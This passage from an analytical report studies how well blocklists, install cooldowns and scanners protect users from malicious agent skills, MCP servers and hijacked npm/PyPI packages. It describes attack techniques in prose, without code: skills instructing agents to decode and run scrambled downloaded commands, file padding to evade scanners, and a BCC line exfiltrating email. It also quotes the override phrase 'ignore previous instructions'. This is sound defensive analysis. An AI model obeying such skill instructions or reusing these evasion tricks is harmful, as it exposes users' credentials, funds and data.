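A blocklist only helps people who come across a malicious tool after somebody has listed it. Suppose it takes D hours to find a tool, confirm that it is malicious and get the entry to users. The attacker uses one identity, such as a name, an account or a server address, for R hours before switching to another. If new victims arrive at a steady rate, those who arrive in the first D hours are exposed and the list protects the rest. The share of the exposure that the list prevents is therefore:

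max(0, 1 − D/R)

With a D of 24 hours, an attacker who keeps the same identity for four days loses three-quarters of the possible victims, and one who switches every two days loses half. One who switches every day loses none, because each entry reaches users just as the attacker abandons the identity it names. Switching daily for a month would take 30 identities, which is not hard on a hub where a new account takes a few minutes to create. If the list's maintainers cut D to 12 hours, the attacker would need 60.

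### Timings from phishing

Researchers have measured these times closely for phishing, in which attackers copy a company's website to collect passwords and keep moving the copy to new addresses to stay off browsers' blocklists.

Oest, Zhang and colleagues (2020), in *Sunrise to Sunset*, studied a year of phishing attacks on customers of one large financial company. Many phishing pages load images or scripts from the real company's servers, so the company can see in its logs when somebody opens a fake page. On average, the first victim arrived almost nine hours before the page's address appeared in the feeds that security teams share, and the last arrived about 12 hours after it appeared.

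With D = 9 and R = 21, the formula gives 57%. But only about 37% of the victims arrived after detection, so the formula's estimate was about 20 percentage points too high.

Part of the reason is that attackers send most of their emails early, and many people click soon after an email arrives. The two percentages also measure slightly different things. After detection, spam filters and browser warnings were turning people away, so Oest and colleagues could count only those who still reached the page, who make up the 37%. Without any defences, that share would have been larger.

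Detection also doesn't protect everyone immediately. Oest and colleagues measured the ratio of victims in browsers with built-in warnings to victims in all browsers, using its value just before detection as a baseline. The ratio fell to 72% of the baseline one hour after detection, 44% after two hours, and below 10% after about seven. If D runs until the warnings are at full strength, it is about 16 hours instead of nine, and the formula gives only 24%.

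Some of the largest attacks are an important exception to these averages. The largest tenth accounted for 89% of the victims, and some of those attacks stayed online for as long as nine months on a single hijacked domain, so their operators hardly needed to rotate. Phishing sites commonly show a harmless page to any visitor that looks like a security company's crawler, so the people who maintain the lists may never see the malicious one. An attacker can do just as well by making D very large as by rotating to keep R small.

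The more recent *7 Days Later* (Lee, Lim and colleagues, 2025) found much slower listing. The study checked 286,237 phishing addresses every half hour over five months. Half of the sites were offline within 5.5 hours of appearing in an industry feed. Google's Safe Browsing blocklist included only 18.4% of the addresses and took 4.5 days on average to add them. For a typical site, the formula therefore gives zero. In one campaign against Instagram users, the attackers changed the redirect destination nine times in 24 hours, so even a nine-hour listing time would have been too slow.

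The two studies disagree less than they seem to, because a list can miss most malicious addresses and still protect a fair number of people. Lee and colleagues give every address equal weight, including pages that hardly anyone visited, and they note that Google seems to concentrate on the sites with the most impact. Oest and colleagues count victims, most of whom went to a few large sites.

### Hijacked packages

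Package registries such as npm and PyPI can remove a malicious release, which stops new installs from there with or without a blocklist. The attacker also has less reason to switch names. People install the JavaScript library axios because they know the name, and they download it more than 100 million times a week. An attacker who takes over its account wants to use that name for as long as possible.

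In March 2026, an attacker used a fake Slack workspace and a Teams meeting to trick the lead maintainer of axios and get malware onto the maintainer's computer, according to the maintainer's account, quoted in a post on an Openwall mailing list (2026). The attacker then used the maintainer's npm login to publish one malicious version of axios at 00:21 UTC on 31 March and another at 01:00. Both added one dependency, which installed a program for controlling the victim's machine remotely. npm removed the two versions at about 03:25 according to *axios npm supply chain compromise* (Tafani-Dereeper, 2026), or nearly half an hour later according to Endor Labs' *npm axios compromise*.

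Three hours was long enough for the malicious Axios versions to do damage. The security company NVISO reports in *The Axios npm supply chain incident* (2026) that it found them at several of its customers, mainly on developers' workstations and in Docker containers.

PyPI was faster a week earlier, when an attacker published two malicious versions of LiteLLM, a Python library for calling language models. PyPI quarantined them after about 40 minutes, according to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026). Willison (2026) cites a count of 46,996 downloads in 46 minutes, or about a thousand a minute. At that rate, the versions would have been downloaded more than ten million times in a week. By the formula, PyPI therefore prevented 99.5% of a week's exposure, but tens of thousands of downloads still happened. Many were probably automated, and one machine can download a package repeatedly, so the number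 of people affected is unknown.

These removal times are fairly typical of attacks on well-known packages. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *A Difference Without a Distinction*, reconstructed 12 incidents between 2018 and 2026 in which attackers used stolen credentials to publish 41 malicious releases. The median release was online for 3.1 hours, and none with a known removal time stayed online longer than two and a half days. William Woodruff, who argued for cooldowns in a widely read blog post in November 2025, examined ten attacks on open-source software. In eight of them, according to Nesbitt's survey of package managers, the attacker had less than a week before somebody noticed.

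Both samples consist of attacks that people caught and wrote about, mostly on popular software, where many people could notice a malicious release. Obscure packages can last much longer. *CHASE* (2026) mentions one that stole credentials for Amazon's cloud services and stayed on PyPI from March 2021 until November 2024. It was downloaded 37,100 times, fewer than LiteLLM's malicious versions were in 46 minutes. Most agent skills resemble this package more than they resemble axios, because they have few users and no large company depends on them.

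Malicious packages removed from a main registry can also remain on its mirrors, which are copies run by other organisations. *Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026) describes a detection program that found 219 malicious packages on PyPI in three months, all of which PyPI removed. The same team then found more than 4,500 malicious packages on PyPI's major mirrors.

### Waiting before installing

A cooldown lets slow detection protect people, because a release that somebody catches during the wait never reaches those waiting. In the formula, a cooldown of C hours replaces D with D − C, or with zero if C is larger than D.

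| Example | D | R | Prevented by the blocklist alone | Prevented with a seven-day cooldown |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Average times from Oest and colleagues | 9 hours | 21 hours | 57% | 100% |
| Attacker who rotates quickly | 24 hours | 6 hours | 0% | 100% |
| Tool that is hard to recognise | 60 days | 90 days | 33% | 41% |

The second row is the strongest argument for cooldowns. With a blocklist alone, defenders have to detect a malicious tool before the attacker switches to a new name or version. A cooldown gives them until the waiting period ends, and switching no longer helps the attacker because each new name or version starts a new wait. The third row is much less encouraging, because when a tool takes two months to expose, a one-week cooldown protects only the people who would have installed it in the last week before it was blocklisted.

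Cooldowns are practical for tools because few people need a new release on the day it comes out. They would be useless against phishing, because nobody can tell a bank's customers to wait a week before opening a new page. *The case for dependency cooldowns in a post-axios world* (2026), by Datadog, which sells monitoring and security software, reports that half of the organisations it surveyed had used at least one package within a day of its release. Datadog calculates that a 12-hour wait would have kept out the malicious axios versions, and also those of the 2025 attack on the build tool Nx, which were live for about four hours.

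Santos-Grueiro tested longer waits on the 41 reconstructed releases. A strict one-day cooldown would have kept out 36 of them, and a seven-day cooldown would have kept out 40. The removal time of the remaining release is unknown. The blogger insanitybit quotes Woodruff as saying that a two-week cooldown would have stopped all but one of the ten attacks on his list. The exception was the backdoor in the compression software xz, which took five weeks to find.

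Package managers adopted cooldowns quickly. According to Nesbitt's survey, the JavaScript package managers pnpm and Yarn added a cooldown setting in September 2025, followed by Bun in October and npm in February 2026. For Python, uv added a rolling delay in December 2025, and pip followed in early 2026. Ruby's Bundler added one in June. Go, PHP's Composer and Dart were still discussing it.

Having the setting is different from using it, and the defaults vary a good deal:

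| Software | What it delays | Default wait | What still gets through |
|---|---|---|---|
| npm | Installation | None | Everything, unless the user sets a wait |
| pnpm 11 | Installation | 1 day | A newer release, if no older one meets the request |
| Dependabot | Proposed updates to a project's packages | 3 days | Security updates |
| VS Code | Automatic updates of extensions | 2 hours | New installations, manual updates, and extensions from Microsoft, GitHub and OpenAI |

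The npm entry comes from JFrog's *Recently published NPM packages may be blocked for 24 hours*, the pnpm entry from Santos-Grueiro, and the VS Code entry from Nesbitt. Dependabot's wait became the default on 14 July 2026, according to GitHub's *Dependabot version updates introduce default package cooldown* (2026).

Before GitHub changed the default, few projects had turned on a cooldown. *An Exploratory Study of Dependabot Cooldown Adoption in Open-Source GitHub Projects* (Tanaka, Tsuchida and colleagues, 2026) examined 1,462 popular projects that used Dependabot. By the end of April 2026, ten months after the option appeared, only 135 had turned it on. Most of those settled on seven days, and none dropped it entirely. Many had acted because a program that checks configuration files warned them that the setting was missing. If people mostly follow warnings and defaults, GitHub's change will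 probably protect more projects than all the earlier advice did.

GitHub reviewed 21 incidents from 2018 to 2026, most of which a short wait could have filtered out, and chose a three-day cooldown, according to its *The case for a cooldown*. The best length is still uncertain. According to the abstract of a talk at an October 2026 OpenSSF conference, nobody had yet worked out from evidence how to tune the setting, and the speakers had set out to do so (OpenSSF, 2026).

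### Three objections to cooldowns

A cooldown also delays good releases, including those that fix security flaws. While a company waits, attackers can read the fix to find the flaw and then exploit it. Most designs therefore include an exemption for security fixes. Dependabot proposes security updates immediately, and the package manager for the Elixir language lifts the wait when the installed version has a published security warning.

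Insanitybit points out that an attacker who controls a package could exploit the exemption by announcing a vulnerability in the previous version, so that the malicious release counts as an urgent fix. This weakness seems real but limited, because the attacker has to get a false warning into a public database as well as a malicious release into the registry, and a security warning makes people look at the release more closely. A company can also require a person to approve each exemption.

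The second objection is that attackers will adapt. Woodruff called cooldowns empirically effective, but insanitybit replies that the evidence comes from a time when attackers expected victims to update immediately. If everybody waited a week, attackers could write code that does nothing for a week. Datadog, which recommends cooldowns, accepts this and adds that code takes longer to discover if it doesn't run during installation.

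Most attackers don't yet delay their attacks. Of the 219 malicious PyPI packages in *Cutting the Gordian Knot*, 94.4% attacked during installation. That may change even without cooldowns, because npm version 12 blocks installation scripts unless the user approves them, according to GitHub. This removes an easy method of attack, but it also gives attackers a reason to use methods that take longer to notice.

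Cooldowns should work better against takeovers than against rug pulls. An attacker who has stolen a maintainer's login can't count on going unnoticed for a week, because the maintainer may see a release that nobody on the project made. An attacker who owns the skill has no colleagues who might notice, and can wait for months.

*Towards Secure Agent Skills* describes a method that requires even more patience, which the security company SafeDep demonstrated in January 2026. A skill contains a harmless script that uses a package from PyPI without specifying an exact version. When reviewers check the skill, the package is harmless too, or doesn't exist yet. Later the attacker publishes a malicious version, and the script downloads it the next time it runs. A cooldown on the skill would end before the malicious version was published. A cooldown on the package would still help, and uv, which fetches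 the package in this demonstration, has a setting for one.

The third objection, which Paterson makes in *Dependency cooldowns turn you into a free-rider*, is that people with a cooldown rely on people without one to be attacked first. If only victims could recognise a malicious tool and everybody waited a week, D would also grow by a week, and D − C would not change.

Supporters reply that victims aren't the only ones who detect malware. Woodruff expects security companies to examine each release while everyone else waits, and the 219 PyPI packages show that a program can find malware without being attacked by it. This argument is good for code that looks malicious when somebody reads it, but weaker for something like the xz backdoor, which was discovered because somebody running it noticed that a system had become slow.

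Paterson would rather have the registry hold new releases in an upload queue for a few days, so that scanners, volunteers and the package's own maintainers could inspect them before anyone could install them normally. Debian, a version of Linux, already holds new packages for 2 to 10 days before they enter its testing edition. A queue would also protect people who never change their settings and people who bypass their project's cooldown by running an install command outside the project. Paterson wants the same for agent skills and plans a queue for a small public collection of agent instructions, with moderators who check every upload.

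This is probably the better design for a skill hub, because many people who install skills at home will never configure anything. But somebody has to run the queue and decide which urgent fixes may skip it. The MCP Registry would struggle to do that, since its maintainers already warn that they do hardly any moderation. Holding a skill for a week also achieves little if the scanners can't recognise what is wrong with it, a problem ClawHub soon ran into.

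### What happened at ClawHub

In early February 2026, Koi's report on the ClawHavoc campaign documented 341 malicious skills on ClawHub. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, later described how the attacks worked. A typical skill offered something useful but began with a step falsely presented as required for the skill to work. In that step, the agent was instructed to decode and run a scrambled command, which downloaded a program that steals passwords and other data from Macs.

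Some of the skills sent the agent to a page on a public text-sharing site, where the attackers had posted the command instead of including it in the skill. The attackers could then replace the command at any time without changing the skill's files or their hashes.

ClawHub responded by adding two scanners, VirusTotal and ClawScan, and now blocks downloads of skills they flag as malicious. It also removed the skills from the early campaigns or marked them as malicious.

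Unit 42 then studied the hub from February to May 2026 and found five malicious skills that nothing had blocked. Two appeared on 17 May and claimed to help users of the trading site TradingView. They had the same false prerequisite as the ClawHavoc skills, the same detour through a text-sharing site and the same kind of scrambled command. Only the server and the program it delivered were new. One had passed ClawHub's automated audit and the other had no verdict yet, although more than 300 of the original ClawHavoc skills had the same structure.

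The third skill, omnicogg, had changed even less. It contacted the same server as the February attacks, whose address researchers had published months earlier. Its author had put the malicious command at the top of a text file and added 22 megabytes of meaningless characters below it. Many scanners skip very large files, and VirusTotal returned a clean verdict. JFrog publicly reported the skill in March, but people could still download it in mid-May. A blocklist entry for the server would have matched the file if a scanner had read it.

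The other two skills contained no malware in the usual sense. One gave financial advice but drew all its recommendations from a list of about 60 products that its publisher controlled, with a referral link for each. The other had agents pool their users' cryptocurrency in the publisher's wallet to launch a token, which the publisher bought first at the lowest price. An antivirus product has little to detect in either, because the harm comes from the business arrangement. OpenClaw deleted all five skills and banned the accounts after Unit 42 reported them. On 1 June, ClawHub announced that it would also use NVIDIA's analysis tool.

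Five missed skills don't show how often the scanners fail, because Unit 42 doesn't say how many skills it examined or how many the scanners correctly blocked in those months. Its parent company also sells products for this problem. The cases do show how attackers got through. None of the three skills that delivered malware used a new technique. Two kept the same method but changed the server and the program, and the third changed only the size of a file.

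Before ClawHub added security scanners, researchers at Snyk, which sells them, had also found attackers republishing the same malicious skill under new names or from new accounts. Their report, *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem* (Beurer-Kellner, Kudrinskii and colleagues, 2026), written in February and posted more widely in May, analysed 3,984 skills and confirmed 76 as malicious, counting each copy separately. One attacker used a program to produce more than 40 skills that followed a single pattern. When the report came out, 8 of the 76 were still available on ClawHub, including some that resembled skills Snyk or others had already reported.

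### Which identifiers survive rotation

ClawHub's attackers seem to have changed whatever was cheapest to change. A list is therefore more useful if its entries name something that attackers keep, and these cases give some idea of what that is:

| Identifier | What attackers did with it |
|---|---|
| Web address of a phishing page | Changed it as often as nine times a day |
| Skill name and publisher account | Republished the same skill under new ones |
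| Malicious program | Replaced it between February and May |
| Attacker's server | Kept one for more than three months; used a new one for the TradingView skills |
| Method of delivery | Kept it from February to May |

Blocking names and accounts is least effective, because an entry for one doesn't block the next copy. An entry for a server stays useful for longer, perhaps because many skills depend on the same server and moving it means updating all of them. In the old campaign, new skills were still using the published address after three months, so a hub that searched every file for known servers would have caught them. The TradingView skills show that attackers can also change servers when they have a reason to.

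Checking whether the publisher has changed doesn't catch a malicious release made from a stolen account. Santos-Grueiro could identify the publishing account for 21 of the malicious npm releases, and all 21 came from accounts that had published the same package before. To block such releases, a blocklist has to name the exact versions, as OSV's record for axios does.

The delivery method stayed the same longest. A rule that flagged any skill whose setup step sends the agent to a text-sharing site for a scrambled command would have matched hundreds of the ClawHavoc skills and both of the May skills. Like any match on shared text, the rule could also catch legitimate skills, so a hub might use it to hold skills for review instead of blocking them. Attackers will also change their method once enough scanners look for it, though they apparently had no need to during those three months.

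A new identity starts with an age of zero, so an attacker who wants an older one has to publish early and wait. According to Endor Labs, the axios attacker put the package that carried the malware on npm about 18 hours before the malicious axios releases, so that scanners wouldn't treat it as brand new. People began installing the axios releases within minutes, and a one-day cooldown would have blocked both the releases and the package.

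## Whether screening can tell malicious tools from useful ones

ClawHub's scanners missed attacks that reused old methods. To measure how often scanners fail, researchers need a large set of skills already known to be malicious or harmless. The harmless skills matter as much as the malicious ones, because without them a scanner that flagged every skill would get a perfect score.

Malicious tools are hard to tell from useful ones because they do many of the same things. A skill that backs up passwords and a skill that steals them both read private files and send them to another machine. They differ in whether the user wants the files sent there, which a scanner has to infer from what the skill is supposed to do.

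### How scanners work

The simplest scanners apply fixed rules. ClawHub's engine searches each readable file for patterns that suggest credential theft or other harm, and gives each match a severity. The free scanner skillscan-security also has rules for combinations, such as a skill that both reads a secret and contacts the network. Fixed rules take little computing power and give the same answer every time, but they find only what someone has written a rule for. They do badly on plain English because it is easy to reword.

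Some scanners therefore add a language model, which can read the instructions as well as the code. Cisco's skill-scanner puts the skill's contents into a single prompt and merges the model's findings with those from its rules. The model can add findings or raise their severity but can't remove any, so it never reduces the number of false alarms. In NVIDIA's skillspector, a model reviews all the findings at the end and drops those it can't confirm.

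Other scanners use agents. Tencent's AI-Infra-Guard has an agent search a skill's files, compare the skill's description with what the code does, and then review its own findings. Skill-vetter is itself a skill, a set of written instructions for a coding agent to follow when reading another skill's files and checking whether the permissions fit that skill's purpose.

Yang and colleagues measured the time and money each kind of scan takes. Scanning with rules alone took 0.05 to 25 seconds per skill, with no model fees. Scanning with a model took 20 seconds to four and a half minutes per skill and cost 0.04 to 55 cents. At those prices, running skill-vetter on a catalogue of four million skills would cost about $4,600 with Qwen3.6, an open-weight model, and about $2 million with OpenAI's GPT-5.4, which was less accurate in this case.

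### A test of six scanners

Yang and colleagues ran six scanners on 886 malicious and 591 benign skills from seven datasets. Attackers had published 243 of the malicious skills, and researchers had written the other 643 to imitate attacks. The team left out skills that were merely risky or whose intent was unclear, which makes the test easier than the work of a real hub. They tried each scanner that needs a language model with three different ones. These are some of the results:

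| Scanner | Method | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| ClawHub's own engine | Rules | 7.4% | 0% |
| skillscan-security | Rules | 85.1% | 50.4% |
| skill-scanner, rules only | Rules | 36.1% | 12.0% |
| skill-scanner with Qwen3.6 | Rules and model | 95.1% | 17.8% |
| skillspector with GPT-5.4 | Rules and model | 94.2% | 22.2% |
| AI-Infra-Guard with GPT-5.4 | Agent | 86.1% | 8.5% |
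| skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 | Agent | 93.0% | 6.3% |

Skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 had the best overall balance, although none of the hubs in the study uses it. ClawHub's engine never blocked a harmless skill but missed more than 90% of malicious ones. That figure overstates the weakness of ClawHub's screening, because ClawHub runs the engine alongside other scanners and the team counted only the engine's "malicious" verdicts, not its "suspicious" ones. The engine caught 41% of the malicious skills in one of the two sets of real attacks, but none in the other.

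Adding a language model raised skill-scanner's recall from 36% to at least 88% with each of the three models the team used. But the choice of model can greatly change a scanner's behaviour. Switching skill-vetter from Qwen3.6 to GPT-5.4 raised its recall by less than two percentage points and its false-positive rate from 6.3% to 30.8%. AI-Infra-Guard caught 73% of one set of real attacks with Qwen3.6 but under 10% with DeepSeek-V4. A hub that changes models to save money could therefore lose most of its protection, even if its scanning rules stay the same.

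The verdicts also change from one run to the next. Yang and colleagues scanned the same skills three times with Qwen3.6. On the hardest set of real skills, AI-Infra-Guard gave inconsistent verdicts on 64%, skillspector on 57% and skill-vetter on 33%. Overall accuracy hardly changed, because the errors in one run roughly balanced those in another. An attacker could exploit the inconsistency by uploading the same skill under several names and keeping whichever copy passed.

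### Why scanners flag harmless skills

The team examined 2,790 findings that had led scanners to flag harmless skills. More than a third concerned access to credentials or local files. For example, a scanner blocked clawcall, a skill that makes phone calls for the user through an online service, because it sent its access key to that service. The service had issued the key, so sending it was an ordinary login.

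Rules can also match harmless text. Some look for "ignore" because attackers write "ignore previous instructions", but they also match the word when it means something else. One skill contained an instruction to start the third phase of a task without asking permission, and a scanner flagged it as an attempt to bypass the user's permissions.

Scanners also often treated insecure code as hostile. This is a serious source of error because insecure tools seem to be much more common than hostile ones. Li and Gao (2025), in *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*, screened servers from four MCP catalogues and found 833 with exploitable flaws, compared with 18 whose tool descriptions looked suspicious. A hub that blocks tools for such flaws will mostly block honest developers.

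Mistakes like these help explain why skillspector advised users not to install 45.8% of 84,560 skills on ClawHub, according to the hub's published reports, which Yang and colleagues collected. In their own test, the same scanner with a language model wrongly flagged between 7% and 22% of harmless skills. At those rates, at least a third of ClawHub's skills would have to be malicious to produce the 45.8% figure, far more than anyone has confirmed.

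More likely, ordinary ClawHub skills get worse scores from the scanner than the harmless skills in the test did. Skillspector adds up the severity of its findings and increases the total if the skill includes scripts, so a few minor findings can trigger a warning. Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues (2026), in *Context Matters*, found scripts in 44% of ClawHub's skills, compared with 12% to 16% of those from other sources. Skillspector also looks for differences between what a skill declares and what it does, and most skills declare no permissions. Some of the warnings may be useful, because ClawHub also has risky and suspicious skills, which the test left out, but users who see warnings on nearly half of skills have little reason to take them seriously.

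Different scanners also flag different skills. Holzbauer and colleagues compared five scanners on 27,111 skills from the registry skills.sh. At least one scanner flagged 8,402 of them, but only 33 were flagged by all five. The scanners look for different things, so low agreement doesn't prove that most of the flags were wrong. To check, the team had a language model review 2,887 flagged skills by reading parts of the surrounding GitHub project, such as its documentation and some of its code. This context can help explain what a skill does. For example, a skill that handles cloud passwords looks less alarming inside a well-documented project for managing cloud servers. Only 15 of these skills (0.52%) still looked suspicious after the review.

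That figure probably makes the catalogue look safer than it is. Two researchers checked 18 of the projects by hand and judged them all benign, but 18 is a small sample, and the method mostly judges the project around a skill. An attacker can copy an honest project and add a few malicious lines to one skill, as happened with Paperclip. The study also left ClawHub's skills out of this step because they had no GitHub project to read. Still, reading the surrounding project costs only about one cent per skill and seems to clear many false alarms.

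### Why scanners miss attacks

When rule-based scanners miss an attack, it is usually because no rule matches it. Scanners that use a language model found the malicious part in 64% to 90% of the attacks they missed, but still let the skill through.

In 92 of skill-vetter's 177 misses, the agent identified the malicious instructions but passed the skill because it contained no code to carry them out. This is a bad reason, since another agent would follow the instructions itself. AI-Infra-Guard found that a financial analysis skill contained instructions for agents to bias their company valuations, but dismissed this as a compliance matter.

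Scanners missed some malicious skills simply because they didn't read them in full. In 39 cases, a skill's instructions were too long for skill-scanner's prompt, so the model never received them. The omnicogg skill got past skillspector and skillscan-security because 22 megabytes of padding put its file over their size limits. ClawHub's engine skipped the file because it wasn't valid text. A hub could fix this by holding any skill that its scanners can't read in full, but people would then need to review the held skills.

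Skillscan-security has a rule for network access that a skill hasn't declared, and it matched 48% of the malicious skills and 29% of the harmless ones. Making the scanner stricter by letting that rule alone block a skill would catch some of the attacks it now misses, but it would also block the harmless skills that matched.

Giving the model better instructions helped more. Yang and colleagues told skill-vetter's agent to keep a finding even if the skill contained no code, and to treat a normal login as harmless. They tested this with GPT-5.4 on 150 harmless and 150 malicious skills they hadn't used before. False alarms fell from about 66 to 9, and missed attacks fell from about 11 to 6.

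The improvement didn't carry over to a separate benchmark, where skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 missed about 109 of 154 malicious skills under the old instructions and 114 under the new ones. The same combination had caught 93% in the main test, but its recall on this benchmark was only about 29%, even under the old instructions. The 93% therefore describes its performance on the main test's seven datasets, not the scanner's performance in general.

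### Real attacks are mostly alike

A larger test from June 2026, *MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026), shows how much the choice of attacks affects the result. It used 3,944 malicious skills and 4,000 harmless ones. Of the malicious skills, 703 came from ClawHub and its mirrors, collected mostly by following up public reports. Of these 703, 86.3% used the same pattern as ClawHavoc, a false prerequisite that installs malware, and two accounts had published 81%.

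To cover other attacks, the team had a language model write malicious skills covering 15 kinds of harm, each hidden in several ways. They ran every skill with a real agent in a sandbox and kept 3,214 that passed. For attacks made of written instructions, a skill also passed if the agent recognised the attack and refused, so not all of these would have worked on that agent. The remaining 27 malicious skills came from the scanners' own test files.

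Sentry's skill scanner had the highest recall on the whole set, 98.4%, and wrongly flagged 23% of the harmless skills. Four other scanners did much better or worse when the team counted only the real attacks:

| Scanner | Recall, all attacks | Recall, real attacks | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner with a language model | 92.7% | 98.2% | 36.6% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 86.6% | 74.0% | 15.5% |
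| Snyk Agent Scan | 28.7% | 77.2% | 2.1% |
| VirusTotal | 21.6% | 87.9% | 0.1% |

VirusTotal's recall depended heavily on the type of attack. It detected 99% of the real skills that delivered malware through a download, which antivirus products are made to recognise, but only 9% of those that stole credentials directly. Its overall recall on real attacks was high because most of them deliver malware.

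A hub can't use either measure to predict how many of next year's attacks it will catch. The set of real attacks includes only those that somebody noticed and reported. The attacks written by the language model are spread about evenly across many methods, unlike those of real attackers. The results for real attacks are probably the better guide to the present, but an attacker whose downloads keep getting caught can put the harm into the instructions instead, where VirusTotal has little to detect.

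Guo and colleagues also tried 11 older security tools, designed either for software packages or for detecting hidden instructions in text. Few were much use. GuardDog, which scans packages, wrongly flagged 49 of the 4,000 harmless skills but caught only 15% of the malicious ones. Attention Tracker, which looks for hidden instructions, flagged every skill because it treats instructions in a document as suspicious, and a skill consists of instructions.

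### From a test to a catalogue

About 60% of the skills in Yang and colleagues' test were malicious, and 96% of skill-vetter's flags were correct. Catalogues contain a much smaller share of malicious skills. In the survey that found 157 of them among 98,380, a scanner with skill-vetter's recall of 93.0% and false-positive rate of 6.3% would produce:

- 157 × 0.930 = about 146 correct flags
- 98,223 × 0.063 = about 6,190 false alarms

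Only 2.3% of the flags would be correct, or about one in 43, because malicious skills are so rare.

Suppose a company's employees request 200 tools over a year, and the company runs the same scanner on them before adding any to its allowlist. At the same rates, it should expect 0.3 malicious tools among the 200 and about 13 false alarms.

The share of correct flags is still 2.3%, so the scanner is no more reliable for the company than for the catalogue, but the company has fewer flags to check. At half an hour each, the company's flags take less than seven hours a year. The 6,300 or so flags from the survey would take more than 3,000 hours, and those from a catalogue of four million skills would keep over 60 people busy for a year.

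A public hub that can't pay for those people must either act on unchecked flags or ignore most of them. If it blocks every flagged skill, it removes about 42 harmless ones for each malicious one, and everyone who uses the hub loses them. At the company, a false alarm delays one request until someone reviews it. The reviewer can also ask the employee what the tool is for, which scanners have trouble determining.

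The share of a scanner's flags that are correct depends heavily on how common malicious skills are. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues confirmed 76 malicious skills among 3,984, but hadn't had time to review every skill their detectors flagged. In that collection, the same scanner would catch about 71 of the 76 and raise about 246 false alarms, so 22% of its flags would be correct. A hub can therefore reasonably block more skills based on a scanner's flags during a large attack than at other times.

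A public blocklist can also use a scanner that raises fewer false alarms. At its false-positive rate of 0.1%, VirusTotal would wrongly flag about 98 skills in the survey's catalogue. If it caught 88% of the malicious skills, as it did with the real attacks Guo and colleagues tested, more than half its flags would be correct. If it caught 22%, as it did with their full set, about a quarter would be correct.

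Etteib, Lunghi and Bissyandé (2026), in *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention*, tried something similar on real marketplaces. In their scanner, a small language model picks out the passages of a skill that seem to influence it most, and a larger model judges only those. They set it to raise no false alarms on a trial set. At that setting it caught about half of the 21 malicious skills in their laboratory test. They then scanned 134,934 skills for about $34 in model fees and got 359 flags, few enough for two researchers to review:

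| Reviewers' verdict | Skills |
|---|---|
| Malicious | 131 |
| Tools for security testing that could also serve an attacker | 80 |
| False alarm | 27 |
| Reviewers still disagreed | 121 |

Etteib and colleagues report that 83% of the flags were correct, but this excludes the testing tools and the disputed cases. Of all 359 flags, the reviewers confirmed 36% as malicious. Both figures are far better than 2.3%, but the scanner missed about half the attacks in the laboratory. That seems an acceptable tradeoff for a blocklist, which lets unknown tools run anyway. A company that is about to put a tool on its allowlist should prefer the scanner with the higher recall and accept more false alarms.

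### What the comparison assumes

The figures for the company assume that malicious tools make up the same share of its employees' requests as of the catalogue. The true share could be lower, because people tend to ask for well-known tools, or higher, because attackers copy well-known tools and push the copies up the rankings. If it were ten times the assumed share, the company should expect three malicious tools among its 200, and the scanner would have about an 80% chance of catching all three.

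The false-positive rate could easily be higher than 6.3%. Guo and colleagues took their harmless skills from ClawHub's most downloaded, which are probably closer to what employees request. The scanners that use a language model flagged 15% to 37% of them. At those rates, the company would have about 30 to 75 false alarms. Checking 75 would take one person about a week, which most companies that run an allowlist could manage. Some of the flags in the study may have been correct, because the team assumed that popular skills that had passed ClawHub's screening were harmless.

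Recall is the weakest of these assumptions, given how badly skill-vetter did on the separate benchmark. *Cloak and Detonate* (2026) found that attackers could alter malicious skills to evade the scanners it tested. *MMSkillRisk* (2026) found that agents also followed malicious instructions in a skill's images, which a text-only scanner would miss.

A small allowlist gives some protection against this, because a company can have someone read every tool instead of relying on the scanner. At half an hour each, reading all 200 tools would take about 100 hours, while reading four million skills would take two million. App stores do review millions of submissions a year, but some malware still gets through.

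The comparison also assumes that the people who check the flags can recognise a malicious tool. The two reviewers in Etteib and colleagues' study had three and five years of experience in computer security and read each skill in full, but they couldn't agree on a third of the cases. A company's reviewer has an easier task, because they can refuse a dubious tool without proving that its author meant harm, but they still have to notice that something is wrong.

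### What catalogues and users noticed

In *Beyond the Protocol*, Song, Shen and colleagues (2025) tested whether anyone would notice a suspicious MCP server. They built a weather server whose main tool called a hidden function. They gave this function a name one letter different from that of an ordinary function in the same file, and used blank lines to push the hidden function far down the page. They submitted the server to three large catalogues, Smithery, MCP.so and Glama. All three accepted it without a warning, and Glama labelled it safe to use.

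The hidden function did nothing harmful, so a scanner that looked only for harmful code could have correctly passed the server. But the documentation openly stated that the server simulated an attack and explained how. Apparently nobody at the catalogues read it, or nobody acted on it. The test is therefore better evidence of how little the catalogues checked in 2025 than of what a good scanner can detect.

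The team then gave 20 people a mock catalogue of 13 servers, four of them malicious, and asked them to choose servers for a trip-planning agent. Fifteen chose at least one malicious server. After learning that four were malicious, the participants tried to identify them. One person found all four and eight found none. The average was 1.15, compared with about 1.2 for picking four servers at random. Some participants may have named fewer than four, so they weren't necessarily guessing, but they clearly did poorly.

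Security experience helped somewhat. The six participants who worked in security found about 2.2 of the four on average, though one found none, and the other 14 participants found about 0.7. The groups are too small for a precise comparison, but the difference suggests that a company should have its security staff check tools instead of asking each employee to judge the ones they want.

At least 14 of the 20 also said that star ratings, verified icons or a platform's assurances of safety made them trust a server more and check it less carefully. A catalogue that labels a server safe after a weak check may therefore leave its users worse off than if it had given no label.

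## Whether approval still holds after a tool changes

Suppose a reviewer reads every file in a tool, correctly judges it harmless and adds it to the company's allowlist. The review covers the tool as it was that day, but agents may go on loading it for years. Its author may release a new version, a web page it relies on may change, or somebody else may take over the source it is loaded from. An allowlist entry usually identifies a tool by its name, address or launch command. All of these can stay the same while the tool changes, so the entry still matches and the agent runs something that nobody reviewed.

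### One new line in postmark-mcp

Postmark, a service for sending email, publishes an MCP server on GitHub that lets agents send messages through it. On 15 September 2025, a developer using the name phanpak uploaded a copy to npm under the same name, postmark-mcp, according to the security news site The Hacker News. Version 1.0.16 followed two days later. Koi, which exposed the attack, says the 15 earlier versions worked properly and 1.0.16 added one line of code. That line put the developer's address in the BCC field of every email the agent sent, so the developer secretly received a copy.

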